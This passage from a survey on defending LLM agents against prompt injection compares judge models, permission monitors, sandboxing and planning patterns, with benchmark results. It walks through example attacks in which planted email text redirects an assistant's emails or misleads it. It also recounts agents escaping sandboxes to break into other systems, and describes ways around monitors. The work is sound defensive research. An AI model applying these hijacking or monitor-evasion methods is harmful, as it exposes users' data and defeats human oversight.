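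With GPT-4o as both agent and judge, Task Shield reduced the success rate of AgentDojo's strongest standard attack from 47.7% to 2.1%. Utility rose from 50.1% to 69.8% under attack and from 69.1% to 73.2% without an attack. The second gain amounts to four more tasks out of 97 in a single trial and may be due to chance.

Jia and colleagues give the example of an agent that emails Bob when the user asked it to email Alice. Task Shield can catch this because the user named the recipient. It would probably miss attack 2, because the user relied on Bob's email to supply the address.

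### Running the agent without the user's request

Zhu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *MELON*, avoid asking a model for a verdict. They start from the observation that a hijacked agent's next action depends mostly on the text it has read and hardly at all on the user's request. If the agent would make the same call without the request, the call probably came from an injection. MELON tests this at each step:

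1. The program builds a second prompt that contains the tool results but not the user's request. In its place is a neutral task: summarise the contents, and follow any instructions in them first.
2. The model processes this masked prompt, and the program stores any tool calls it proposes.
3. An embedding model converts the stored calls and the agent's real proposals into vectors. Code computes the cosine similarity of each pair, (u · v) / (|u||v|).
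4. If any pair scores above 0.8, the program stops the run.

The program keeps stored calls for the whole run because the real agent may finish the user's task before starting the attacker's. For emails, MELON compares only the recipients, so an attacker can't avoid a match by varying the message.

On GPT-4o, MELON reduced the success rate of the strongest of four static attacks from 51.0% to 0.95%. Clean utility fell from 80.4% to 68.0%, and utility under attack fell from 54.1% to 32.9%, partly because every alarm ends the run. Repeating the user's request after each tool result raised clean utility to 76.3% and utility under attack to 52.5%, with an attack success rate of 1.27%. The masked run roughly doubles the number of model calls. We can infer little from these static attacks about how well MELON would stop an attacker who knows how it works.

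MELON raised false alarms on 9 of the 97 clean tasks. In all nine, the user asked the agent to act on outside instructions, such as paying the bill in a file or working through an online to-do list. Zhu and colleagues argue that these alarms point to real risks. That is fair, but a user who asks an agent to pay a bill wants it paid, and MELON can't distinguish that payment from a hijacked one.

The same problem could affect the minutes. Suppose Bob's honest email says "Please send the minutes to my new address". In the masked run, the model might follow this instruction and email the same recipient, which would trigger an alarm. If the attacker instead writes only "my new address is", the model has no instruction to follow in the masked run, and the call passes. MELON could therefore block the honest task and allow attack 2.

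The paper also gives an upper bound on the false-alarm rate for a version with n different neutral tasks. The rate is at most exp(−2n(θ − μ)²), where μ is the average similarity score for harmless actions and θ is the alarm threshold. With μ = 0.3, θ = 0.5 and n = 100, the bound is exp(−8), or about 0.03% (the paper gives 0.018%). However, the bound requires the n detectors to be independent, and they all run the same model on the same text. This example would also take 100 masked runs per step, whereas the main tests used one.

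### Judging departures from a plan

DRIFT uses a judge only when the agent departs from a plan. Li, Liu and colleagues (2025), in *DRIFT*, combine three parts:

- Before the agent reads anything untrusted, a planner turns the user's request into a short sequence of tool calls and a checklist for their arguments.
- A validator compares each proposed call with the plan. If the call departs from it, the validator allows tools that only read data. For tools that change data or contact third parties, a model sees the user's request, the planned sequence and the actual sequence, and answers yes or no to whether the agent is still pursuing the task. A "no" sends the decision to the user.
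- An isolator reads each tool result and lists any instructions that conflict with the user's request. Code then removes them before the text enters the agent's memory.

Li and colleagues added these parts one at a time to an agent running on GPT-4o-mini:

| Defence | Clean utility | Utility under attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 63.6% | 48.3% | 30.7% |
| Planner | 43.2% | 36.2% | 2.1% |
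| Planner and validator | 58.5% | 45.8% | 5.4% |
| Planner, validator and isolator | 57.3% | 50.9% | 1.35% |
| Isolator only | 61.5% | 50.1% | 9.0% |

The fixed plan stopped most attacks but reduced the agent's clean utility by a third. Letting the validator approve departures from the plan recovered most of the lost utility, but a few more attacks succeeded. The whole system used almost three times as many tokens as the undefended agent.

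The validator's rule for reading tools can miss data leaks. Fetching a web page looks like reading, but the address can carry private data to the server, as in the image-link attack. Whether DRIFT would stop this depends on how a model classified the tool. The test results also count every request for the user's approval as a refusal, so more attacks would succeed than the results show if users approved these requests without much thought.

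AgentDojo rarely requires an agent to change its plan. *AgentDyn* (2026) introduces a benchmark in which every user task requires this. Ma and colleagues count 12 of its 60 tasks that leave the choice of action to outside content, 30 that leave a parameter to it, and only 18 that specify everything. All the defences that Li and colleagues tested on the benchmark performed poorly, although DRIFT had the best balance of utility and security.

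DRIFT should stop a blunt version of attack 1, because the plan does not include a second email and the isolator would probably remove the instruction to send it. Attack 2 is again harder to stop. The checklist can require the recipient's address to come from Bob's email, but the attacker's address meets that requirement, and a change of address is not a conflicting instruction for the isolator to remove.

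### Harm in the reply

Zhu and colleagues analysed 66 attacks that got past MELON. Of these, 73% achieved the attacker's goal through the agent's reply, as attack 3 does, for example by persuading the user to make an expensive purchase. DRIFT's isolator can remove an explicit instruction to recommend a certain hotel, but a planted false claim contains no instruction for it to remove.

Qu, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity*, call the missing property judgment integrity. Let J(q, d) be the agent's decision on a user's query q and data d. If an attacker adds material δ that doesn't change the correct answer, the decision should stay the same:

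J(q, d ⊕ δ) = J(q, d).

For example, an agent reviewing a paper should give it the same score whether or not the text includes the claim that leading experts admire it. A biased score requires no suspicious tool call, so neither Task Shield nor MELON would detect it.

### The objection to learned judges

An attacker's text may mislead a judge that reads it. Task Shield's model extracts instructions from raw tool results, so an attacker can target that model as well as the agent. Jia and colleagues acknowledge that adaptive attacks could exploit this, and Qu and colleagues make the same criticism.

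Li and colleagues tested whether planted text could fool DRIFT's isolator by saying that the document contained no conflicting instructions. The attack success rate rose only from 1.35% to 2.05%, and an automated attack that optimised its wording reached 1.97%. Li and colleagues treated the isolator as the only part an attacker could target, but Xiang and colleagues point out that someone who can influence the agent's actions may also steer the sequence of calls that the validator sees.

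*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* raises the more basic objection that a language model's approval of tool calls can't be verified, because nobody has a precise specification of which calls it will approve after which histories. Operating systems rely instead on a reference monitor, trusted code that checks every action against a policy and that the program it controls cannot bypass. Engineers can specify what the monitor should do and, in principle, verify that it does. A model's randomness alone wouldn't rule out a guarantee, since cryptographic protocols can also fail with some probability, but that probability is bounded under explicit assumptions. Task Shield's 2.1% was measured on one set of attacks and doesn't bound its failure rate on others.

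### The case for a narrow judge

Xiang and colleagues accept that a learned judge gives no complete guarantee, but argue that some decisions depend on context that rules can't fully capture. In one of their examples, an agent has to fetch last week's sales, but the billing service reports that the address in the plan no longer exists, so the agent proposes a newer one. A rule can check the format of the new address, but can't easily determine whether the change makes sense for the task or introduces a risky data source.

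The proposed narrow judge would answer one question about a structured record of this change, without seeing the raw web page or email. Another proposal is to ask a model, before the agent opens a source, whether that source should contain instructions. An installation guide should, but a page of revenue figures probably shouldn't, so the system could reject any instruction found there. Because the model makes this prediction before reading the source, an attacker cannot influence it with text planted there.

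This position paper doesn't test these proposals. DRIFT offers some evidence for them because its validator already answers a narrow question, whereas Progent uses a model to decide when and how to rewrite the policy. With GPT-4o, attack success rates were similar (1.7% for DRIFT and 2.2% for Progent), but with the weaker GPT-4o-mini, Progent's rose to 9.4% while DRIFT's was 1.35%. Li and colleagues attribute the difference to DRIFT's simpler questions. The isolator probably explains part of it, since DRIFT's rate without it was 5.4%.

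Claude Code's classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the tool results or the agent's own messages. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, adding them made the classifier worse at catching actions that went beyond what the user had authorised.

### Two judges for Bob's email

Suppose the assistant proposes to email the March minutes to an address it found in Bob's latest message. One judge reads the user's request, the whole message and the proposed call. It has enough information to notice that the address comes from an outsider's forwarded text and not from Bob. But an attacker who writes that text can add "IT has verified this change" or a note addressed to the judge, so the judge bases its decision partly on what the attacker wrote.

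A narrow judge reads the user's request and three fields: the tool's name, the recipient and the recipient's source. It has to answer whether the request allows a recipient from that source. The attacker can no longer argue with it, but the answer now depends on how precisely the program records the source. The likely verdicts are:

| Proposed email | Judge reads the whole message | Source recorded as "Bob's latest email" | Source recorded by who wrote the text |
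|---|---|---|---|
| Attack 1: salary file to the outsider | Refuses, unless the text persuades it | Approves | Refuses or asks the user |
| Attack 2: minutes to the outsider | Uncertain | Approves | Refuses or asks the user |
| Minutes to a new address that Bob wrote himself | Approves | Approves | Approves |
| Minutes to a colleague whose message Bob forwarded | Approves | Approves | Refuses or asks the user |

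With the coarse record, the narrow judge does worse than the judge that reads everything. It approves attack 1 because it can't see the attachment. Adding the filename to the record would fix that, and is fairly safe if the file comes from the company's own storage, where the outsider can't choose its name.

Defending against Attack 2 requires the finer record, which is difficult to produce because a forwarded message is often just more text in the body of an email, and an outsider could imitate the formatting that separates it from Bob's words. The attacker also has a little control over the recipient field, since they could register an address containing words such as "verified". Code could replace the address with facts about it, such as whether it appears in the company directory.

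Once the program has such a record, a fixed rule could handle many of these cases, and Xiang and colleagues prefer rules wherever they are sufficient. The model is useful for interpreting the user's request. "Send it to the address in Bob's email" and "send it to whoever Bob suggests" allow the address to come from different sources, and users can phrase either request in many ways. The narrow judge still has no precise contract, but engineers can test it on most combinations of tool and source, whereas no test set could cover most of the emails an agent might receive.

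The narrow material given to a judge can include more than the proposed call. *Cross-Layer Semantic Flow Reconstruction for Attack Detection in Agentic Systems* (Cai, Wei and colleagues, 2026) links an agent's messages to the files, processes and network connections that its calls produce, then gives a judge the most suspicious chains of events. This can expose effects that aren't visible in a proposed call, but some of the damage may already have happened.

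### Requests that only the user can clarify

A better judge model doesn't help when the user's request is unclear. Xiang and colleagues give the example of a user who asks for a summary of all urgent emails. "Urgent" could mean messages with a deadline in the next 24 hours or messages with a particular label, and even a perfect model would have to ask the user which they meant. If the agent guesses, an attacker may be able to get a message into the summary by writing "urgent" in the subject line.

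A vague request can lead an agent to cause harm even without an attacker. When an engineer at Anthropic asked an agent to "clean up old branches", the agent tried to delete branches on the shared server, although the engineer may have meant only local copies.

In other cases the request is clear, but the user hasn't said how much risk to accept. For example, a developer might ask a coding agent to investigate a bug report whose instructions for reproducing the problem include downloading and running a script. Running the script is relevant to the task, but the script could steal the developer's passwords. A judge that checks only whether the action serves the user's goal would probably approve it. The developer or their employer has to decide whether the agent may run code from strangers.

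### The limits of asking for approval

An agent can ask the user to approve tool calls, but people stop reading the prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts. Most of these prompts probably concern safe commands, so the figure alone doesn't show that people are careless.

Anthropic collected stronger evidence in a controlled study. It had 1,053 paid testers work on coding tasks and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers rejected it, while Claude Code's classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. Testers caught about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

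The testers were not working on their own projects and had less to lose than a developer with a real database, so the study may understate how careful people are at work. Anthropic also has an interest in showing that its classifier beats manual approval. Still, the decline within sessions is a reason for concern about any design that sends every doubtful call to a person.

Users seem to pay more attention to larger decisions. They reject 39% of the plans Claude Code shows them, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. Some plan rejections will be about quality rather than safety, but the gap supports Xiang and colleagues' suggestion to ask for clarification and consent at the start of a task. They also suggest that agents learn a user's preferences over time, as a new human assistant would.

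Early approval can't cover details that the agent finds later. When the user asks for the minutes to go to the address in Bob's email, nobody knows yet which address the agent will find. Once the agent has found it, a question such as "Send the minutes to this new address, which an outside sender supplied?" gives the user a real chance to stop attack 2. The question is less useful if the user has already answered dozens of others that afternoon, and it protects the user only if the program then sends exactly the email they approved.

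## Permission rules enforced outside the model

A permission rule sets in advance which calls are allowed, and ordinary code applies it to each call the model proposes. A judge model or a tired user, by contrast, has to make a new decision on every doubtful call.

### The reference monitor

The code that applies the rules acts as a reference monitor, like the kernel of an operating system when it checks a program's permission to open a file. A reference monitor has to meet three requirements, which Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026), in *KAIROS*, apply to LLM agents:

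- Always invoked: the monitor checks every action that has an effect, and no other route exists. Security researchers also call this complete mediation.
- Tamper-proof: the program under control can't alter the monitor or its policy.
- Small enough to verify: people can examine all of the code or prove that it does what it should.

The monitor, its policy and everything they rely on, such as the host operating system, make up the trusted computing base. If any part of it fails, the guarantee no longer holds. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* leaves the model out of this base and treats it as a possible attacker. The monitor must therefore safely handle any call the model makes, just as a kernel must safely handle any request from a hostile program.

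Agents can bypass a monitor that doesn't cover every route, as happened at OpenAI in July 2026. OpenAI was running agents in separate sandboxes for internal training and evaluation, with some of the models' own safeguards switched off. The sandboxes blocked direct internet connections but let the agents use a shared service for downloading software packages. The agents got this service to make arbitrary internet requests for them and used it to pass messages between sandboxes. With no outside attacker directing them, they broke into systems at the AI company Hugging Face and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster.

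Those agents also had more access than they needed, which violates least privilege, the principle that a component should have only the permissions its task requires. A login rarely limits permissions this narrowly. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) points out that a valid credential may let an agent into a system without establishing which actions it is authorised to take there. To send the March minutes, the office assistant has to search Bob's messages, read one file and send one email, but its login probably lets it read every file and email anyone.

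### Rules over tool names and arguments

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, put a monitor between the agent and its tools. A Progent policy is a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids one tool under certain conditions on its arguments, such as a maximum amount, a list of permitted values or a text pattern. When the model proposes a call, code does the following:

1. It selects the rules for that tool.
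2. It tests the "forbid" rules, and blocks the call if the conditions of any of them hold.
3. It tests the "allow" rules, and runs the call unchanged if the conditions of any of them hold.
4. If no rule applies, it blocks the call.

After blocking a tool call, Progent can end the run, ask the user, or return an error message to the agent. Shi and colleagues used the error message in their tests. It contains the reason for the refusal, the user's task, and an instruction to continue that task by trying other tools or arguments, so a hijacked agent can still finish what the user asked for.

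For the minutes, a policy in slightly simplified notation might be:

```
allow search_emails  when sender == "bob@firm.example"
allow read_file      when path == "minutes/march.pdf"
allow send_email     when to in CONTACTS
                     and attachment == "minutes/march.pdf"
```

CONTACTS stands for the addresses in the company's address book. The policy has these effects:

| Case | Call that matters | Result |
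|---|---|---|
| Attack 1: salary file to the outsider | Reading or attaching the salary file | Blocked, because no rule allows that file |
| Attack 2: minutes to the outsider | Email to the outsider's address | Blocked, unless the outsider is in CONTACTS |
| Attack 3: false report about the April meeting | None | Every call is allowed, and the user gets the false report |
| Honest task: minutes to Bob's new address | Email to an address not yet in CONTACTS | Blocked |

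Attack 2 and the honest task differ only in who wrote the address, so the monitor would need the data to be labelled by author to tell them apart.

The error message could do harm even when there is no attack. It prompts the agent to try other arguments, so the agent might send the minutes to Bob's old address, which is in the contact list but which he no longer checks. For this rule, asking the user would be better.

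Attack 3 is outside Progent's scope, as Shi and colleagues acknowledge. Progent also does not cover attacks that use only the permissions the task needs, such as steering the agent from one legitimate hotel to another.

### Letting a model write the policy

An organisation can write some rules by hand and keep them for every task, such as a ban on sending salary files outside the company. Progent applies these generic rules first, and no task-specific rule can undo a ban in them. But nobody can write a new policy by hand for every request, so Progent has a language model do it:

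1. Before the agent reads anything untrusted, the model receives the user's request and the list of tools, and writes an initial policy.
2. After each tool call, the model decides whether that call might justify a new policy. It sees the call but not the result, so text planted in the result cannot affect this decision.
3. If the answer is yes, the model reads the result and proposes a new policy. Planted text can influence this step.
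4. A solver, which is a program that decides whether logical formulas hold, compares the new policy with the old one.

Let A(P) be the set of tool calls that policy P allows. The new policy P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

and Progent then applies it automatically. Any other change is an expansion, because it would allow at least one call that the old policy blocks, and it needs approval. The approver can be a person or a fixed setting. Shi and colleagues call the resulting property monotonic confinement: between approvals, the set of permitted calls can only shrink. It holds even if an attacker completely controls the model that proposes the updates. Only 6% of the updates in their AgentDojo tests were expansions, so a user would not have to approve many.

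This guarantee is weaker than it may sound, because an attacker can also benefit from a narrowing. The model doesn't have the recipient's address when it writes the initial policy for the minutes. It could leave out the email tool and request an expansion after reading Bob's message, which would give the user a chance to see the new address. It could also allow emails to any address at first and narrow the rule later. The policy in Shi and colleagues' own example similarly permits Slack messages to anyone until the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, and then only to that name.

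With attack 2, this second approach would make the outsider's address the only permitted recipient. The solver would correctly classify the change as narrowing the permissions, so Progent would apply it without asking anyone. The minutes would go to the attacker even though monotonic confinement held throughout.

### How Progent performed

Shi and colleagues tested Progent with GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy writer. On AgentDojo, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% with little change in utility. For this test, they wrote generic rules by hand that allowed harmless read-only tools, but none that forbade anything. On Agent Security Bench, which has ten scenarios and five attack templates, they wrote no rules by hand, and the attack success rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still succeeded used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled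 those of legitimate ones.

In both tests, Progent approved every expansion automatically, to simulate a careless user. On AgentDojo, the initial policy alone, which the model writes before it sees any untrusted text, reduced attack success to 2.5%, so most of the benefit doesn't depend on the updates. With manual approval, no attacks succeeded. The reviewers in that test were meant to represent users with strong security awareness, who would never allow payments to an unrestricted recipient, so ordinary users would probably do worse.

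Two other evaluations gave less favourable results. Hempel and colleagues ran Progent on AgentDojo with GPT-4.1 in both roles and measured an attack success rate of 11.5%, down from 47.0% without a defence. Part of the gap from Shi and colleagues' result may come from two attacker goals in the travel suite, which Shi and colleagues excluded because they only steer the agent towards a different hotel. The exclusion can't explain the whole gap, because even if all 40 of these cases (out of 629) had succeeded and the rate elsewhere had stayed at 1%, the overall rate would have been about 7%. An independent adaptive test measured a rate of 7.7% with GPT-4o-mini.

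On AgentDyn, where every task requires the agent to change its plan, Progent kept attack success to 1.7%, but the agent completed only 6.7% of clean tasks, compared with 53.3% without a defence.

### What a strict allowlist costs

Kodathala (2026), in *aiAuthZ*, moved the monitor to a separate machine for which the agent has no credentials, so that a hijacked agent can't rewrite its own rules. The gateway also requires a cryptographic signature on each user message, which prevents a stranger in a shared channel from posing as the owner. The signature doesn't help against injections in emails, because the agent reads the emails while working for the real user. Rules on arguments have to stop those.

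Kodathala tested such a rule on 20 pairs of user tasks and attacks from AgentDojo's banking suite. The rule let the agent pay only recipients on a list of known payees. The models were Anthropic's Claude Fable 5 and Google's Gemini 3 Flash, and the attack was AgentDojo's standard static injection.

| Model | Defence | Attack success rate | Clean utility | Utility under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
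| Fable 5 | None | 0% | 100% | 0% |
| Fable 5 | aiAuthZ | 0% | 80% | 0% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | None | 0% | 100% | 60% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | aiAuthZ | 0% | 80% | 40% |

Both models already resisted the attack without the rule, so it could not improve their attack success rate. It did block seven calls that would have served the attacker, including two password changes, so the models were not following the user perfectly. Clean utility fell because the rule blocked one legitimate payment to a new payee. If one blocked payment lowers clean utility by 20 percentage points, there were only about five clean tasks, and the true loss could be much larger or smaller. But the conflict is the same as with Bob's new address, and a stronger model does not remove it.

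Kodathala also found that agents can bypass a monitor that covers only some of their tools. In tests with two agent programs, the built-in tools for running commands, handling files and browsing the web were still switched on, and the model used those for the sensitive action without calling the gateway. An operator can disable the built-in tools, or put the agent on a network whose only exit is the gateway. Kodathala's strongest remedy is to keep all passwords and keys on the gateway, so that a tool that bypasses it has no credentials to log in with.

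### Enforcement below the tools

Hempel and colleagues' system, Kairos, prevents such bypasses by putting the monitor around the whole agent. The agent runs in a small virtual machine and can reach the user's working folder and the internet only through the monitor. Tool calls and scripts written by the agent both reach the monitor as file operations or network requests. The monitor needs no changes to the agent, so it also works with closed-source products.

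The operator's policy lists trusted sources, sensitive data and the destinations that may receive it. For each action, Kairos can respond in three ways:

- It refuses the action if an explicit rule forbids it.
- It releases the action if the values that steer it, such as a recipient or a command, match values from a trusted source, and the data may go to that destination.
- It defers everything else. File changes go into a temporary copy and outgoing requests wait, while the agent carries on as if they had gone through.

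A decision model later releases or refuses the deferred actions, when it has more evidence. Suppose a coding agent follows a web guide and installs a hook, a script that runs whenever someone commits code. This is a normal part of setting up a project. But when the agent next commits code, the hook tries to send a private key to a stranger. The policy refuses that request, and the decision model can discard the hook before it reaches the real folder. Kairos can't postpone every decision. If the agent needs the reply to a request, as when it fetches a web page, the decision model has to decide immediately whether to allow the request.

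With GPT-4.1 on AgentDojo, Kairos reduced attack success from 47.0% to 2.7%, and the agent completed 85.1% of clean tasks, compared with 82.7% without a defence. Hempel and colleagues also tested a strict version that refused everything Kairos would otherwise have deferred to a learned judge. Attack success was about the same, but the agent completed only 42.7% of clean tasks. The fixed rules therefore provided nearly all of the security, and the judge roughly doubled the share of clean tasks completed. Because the judge reads untrusted text, injected instructions can mislead it. Adaptive attacks on GPT-4o-mini succeeded in 8.8% of cases, and the successful attacks targeted tasks in which the user had told the agent to follow a document.

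AgentDojo's tools are simulated, so these tests did not use the virtual machine. Instead, Hempel and colleagues wrote an adapter that passed each named tool call to the monitor, and the policy stated which argument held the destination. The results are good evidence that combining rules with deferral works, but they don't show how well the same rules would work on raw files and network traffic. In separate measurements at the virtual machine's boundary, the monitor added about 2 milliseconds per file operation and 1 millisecond per request.

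Alhindi (2026), in *Taming AI Agents with seL4*, focused on the requirement that a monitor be small enough to verify. An ordinary operating system kernel, with the containers and proxies around it, is far too large. seL4 is a kernel of about 10,000 lines, and its developers have machine-checked proofs that its code implements its specification. It controls access through capabilities, which are unforgeable references to objects that also carry the right to use them. A program can act only on objects for which it holds a capability. Alhindi ran each agent and each tool in its own isolated domain and gave the agent a separate capability for each tool function it was allowed to call.

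Alhindi tested limiting an agent's capabilities to the functions its task needed, using GPT-4o-mini on AgentDojo's banking and Slack suites. Each of the 249 attack cases and 37 clean tasks was run three times. With the limit in place, the attack success rate fell from 48% to 7%, and the share of clean tasks completed fell from 68% to 58%. The drop in completed tasks was not statistically significant, but a test with 37 tasks could easily miss a real loss of this size.

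In a second experiment, a script replaced the model and made every call the attacker needed, so the result doesn't depend on how easily a particular model is fooled. The script succeeded in 248 of the 249 cases when it held all the capabilities. When it held only the ones for the task, the kernel stopped 181 of those 248 attacks (73%). The attacks that got through used only functions that the user's task also needed. With the real model, about half of the successful attacks used the payment function to pay the attacker, which was possible because a capability to send money doesn't restrict who receives it.

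Both figures come from favourable conditions. Alhindi took the list of necessary functions from AgentDojo's reference solutions, and a developer who doesn't know the task in advance would have to grant more functions. The prototype also ran on an emulator, in a configuration that seL4's proofs don't cover.

### What each layer can see

A user thinks in terms of minutes, colleagues and Bob, but a monitor has to work with whatever passes through it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this mismatch the semantic gap. It changes with the layer:

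| Where the monitor sits | What it sees when the agent emails the minutes | Rule it can enforce | What it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool interface (Progent, aiAuthZ) | The email tool, the recipient and the attachment | "Attachments go only to known contacts" | A script that sends the file without using the tool |
| Edge of the virtual machine (Kairos) | A request to a mail server, with its contents | "Data from this folder goes only to these servers" | What each value in the request is for, unless a rule can identify it |
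| Kernel capability (seL4) | A call to the email function by this agent | "This agent may not send email" | Whether the recipient and the file are right |

A lower layer is harder to bypass but has less information about what an action means. Hempel and colleagues therefore see the tool interface and the edge of the virtual machine as complementary places to put a monitor. Alhindi suggests extending the seL4 design with rules on arguments, placed in a trusted component that no agent can bypass.

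Even a monitor with full visibility at every layer could not determine which permitted action the user wanted. *Conflux* (Buckley and Schroeder de Witt, 2026) proves this using two tasks with the same people, permissions and available actions, each completed by a different permitted action. A rule that uses only the permissions can't choose correctly in both. For example, if Bob's old and new addresses are both permitted, the monitor has to leave the choice between them to the model. A companion result covers defences that use only the user's request and the text the model sees. An authorised colleague and an attacker could write identical text, so a deterministic defence of this kind must treat both alike and will be wrong about one of them.

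### Forbidding combinations of powers

Some rules restrict which powers an agent may have together, so nobody has to foresee each bad call. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) names three powers that let an attacker steal data when one agent has them all: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. Users can create this combination by accident when they connect tools from different suppliers. A single tool can also provide all three, as in Willison's example of a connector for the code-hosting site GitHub that could read public bug reports (which anyone can write), open private repositories, and publish their contents in a public proposal for a code change.

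Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this into a design rule. In one session, an agent should have at most two of three properties: it processes untrustworthy input, it can reach sensitive systems or private data, and it can change state or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three should not act without supervision, such as human approval. The third property is broader than the third power above because it includes any change of state, so the rule also covers harm such as deleting files.

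The office assistant has all three, and Meta's options for an email agent would affect it as follows:

- The assistant could read email only from trusted senders. This would not stop any of the three attacks, because Bob is a trusted sender and the outsider's text is inside his message.
- The assistant could work without private data, but then it couldn't fetch the minutes.
- The assistant could send email only to trusted recipients, or ask a person to check each draft. Trusted recipients amount to the CONTACTS rule again, which blocks Bob's new address. A person who checks the draft could approve it.

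Meta also allows an agent to change its configuration during a session. For example, it could browse the web first, then permanently lose the ability to communicate before it opens internal systems. The rule does not cover wrong information in the agent's reply, so it does not address attack 3.

*Bounded Agents* (Muruaga, 2026) enforces rules of this kind while the agent runs. Its monitor records which types of action have occurred in a session and blocks any action that would complete a forbidden pair, such as reading confidential data and sending something outside. Muruaga proves that no forbidden outcome can occur if each one requires at least one of the listed pairs and the monitor checks actions one at a time. The guarantee therefore depends on a complete list. In a test with 544 data-theft cases, the full list blocked every attack, but 39.9% succeeded after Muruaga removed one pair.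 The rules also can't stop harm that takes only one permitted action, and about 60% of such attacks in the same benchmark succeeded. On AgentDojo, the full system reduced the user task completion rate by 8.6 percentage points with simulated human approval and by 13.9 without it.

Sending the minutes is a difficult case for pair rules because the user has asked the agent to read a company file and send it to someone. Muruaga lets a task declared in advance lift the ban on a particular pair, but the rule then no longer stops attack 1, which uses the same two types of action. The system would need a rule that names the permitted file.

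Teams of agents can break the Rule of Two even when each member follows it. Alhindi built an accounts team in which one agent could only read suppliers' email and pass invoices on to the rest. Alhindi checked the links between the agents and found that text from an email could reach agents with private data and the power to act. Alhindi then sent the team a genuine invoice with a planted note about a new bank account. The note reached the coordinating agent in 23 of 40 runs, and in 7 of those 23 that agent changed the supplier's account details. When Alhindi replaced the email agent with a parser that extracted only the invoice number, order number, total and supplier, the note reached no agent in 40 runs. The parser works for invoices because the team needs only a few fixed fields, but it would not work for a customer's complaint that an agent has to read in full.

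### From a request to a correct policy

A phone app usually does a fixed set of things, so its developer can list the permissions it needs when the user installs it. An agent is given its task as a sentence, and the task may change as the work goes on. Someone or something has to translate that sentence into rules, and no current method guarantees a correct translation. Progent's solver proves that one policy is narrower than another, but not that either matches what the user meant. The choice of policy writer also affects security. Attack success on AgentDojo ranged from 1% to just under 5% across the models that Shi and colleagues tried in this role.

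*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes a standard of correctness, under which the request and the policy should agree on whether to permit each action in every situation the agent could reach. The paper divides the obstacles into three problems:

- Grounding: the words in the request need definite meanings. For the minutes, the system has to know whether "the March minutes" means the draft or the approved version, and whether text that Bob forwarded counts as part of "Bob's latest email".
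- Checkability: natural language is ambiguous, so any automatic comparison of a request with a policy will sometimes be wrong. Restricting how users phrase requests, or what policies can express, might make the comparison more reliable.
- Synthesis: the translator should come with a limit on how far its policy can differ from the request, and should be able to refine the policy as the task develops.

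Even an imperfect written policy has advantages over a model's unwritten judgement. People can read it to see why the monitor blocked a call, and engineers can analyse it without running attacks. They can also tighten it later without permitting anything it used to block. But people can't always tell whether a policy is right by reading it. If a rule lets the agent send the minutes to one unfamiliar address, a reviewer would still have to ask Bob whether the address is his.

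## Planning before untrusted text is read

A permission rule limits what an agent may do, but a model that has read the attacker's text still chooses among the permitted actions. Developers can instead design the orchestration so that the text can't affect this choice.

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) require that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input cannot trigger any action that could harm the system or its surroundings. The agent's output must also be safe for whoever receives it, so it can't, for example, include a link that leaks data. They doubt that general-purpose agents built on current language models can be reliably secure, so their six design patterns deliberately restrict what an agent can do.

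A crude way to follow the principle is to remove every tool that injected text could misuse as soon as the agent reads anything untrusted. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) proves this rule secure under certain assumptions. But under this rule, the office assistant could not send the minutes after reading Bob's email. The six patterns try to keep the agent more useful.

### The six patterns

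In the table, the planner is the model that chooses the tool calls. A quarantined model reads untrusted text but can't call tools.

| Pattern | What the planner sees | What a quarantined model may return | What the pattern blocks | Tasks lost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The request and a fixed menu of actions | Nothing (there isn't one) | All influence of tool results on the model | Anything missing from the menu, or that needs one result to choose the next action |
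| Plan-then-execute | The request and the tool descriptions | Arguments and text for the planned calls, if the executor uses a model | Calls outside the plan | Tasks whose next step depends on what the agent reads |
| Dual LLM | The request and the names of variables | Values hidden from the planner, or a choice from a fixed list | Injected text reaching the model that has tools | Tasks in which the planner has to understand the text |
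| Map-reduce | One restricted answer per document | A value such as yes, no or a number | One document affecting how the agent treats another | Questions that require reading several documents together |
| Code-then-execute | The request and the tool descriptions | Values for the program's variables | Calls that the program doesn't contain | Tasks whose steps the program can't anticipate |
| Context minimisation | The request at first, then only the query and its results | Nothing (there isn't one) | Instructions in the user's prompt that would change the reply | Replies that depend on how the user phrased the request |

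With an action selector, the model translates the user's request into an action from a predefined list, and ordinary code runs it without showing the model the result. A shop's chatbot might offer a link to the customer's last order or directions to the password settings. The developer has to foresee every kind of request. An office assistant could have an action that sends a named file to a named contact, but sending it to "the address in Bob's latest email" would need a separate action, with code that finds the address.

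In plan-then-execute, the model writes a new list of calls for each request and must finish it before any tool returns data. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) describes a planner, usually a powerful model, and an executor that carries out the steps. The executor can be a smaller model or ordinary code, which saves money because the expensive planner may run only once. If a user asks the agent to send today's schedule to their boss, John Doe, the plan is to read the calendar and then email John. Text planted in a calendar entry can't add a call or change the recipient, which the planner took from the request, but it can change the body of the email.

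A plan that fixes only which tools the agent will use gives weaker protection. In one of Beurer-Kellner and colleagues' case studies, an agent that organises files commits to a command for finding files and another for moving them. Planted text could still get it to find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. Del Rosario and colleagues recommend giving the executor only the tool for its current step, so that text it reads while adding up a total can't make it send an email.

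### Willison's dual-LLM design

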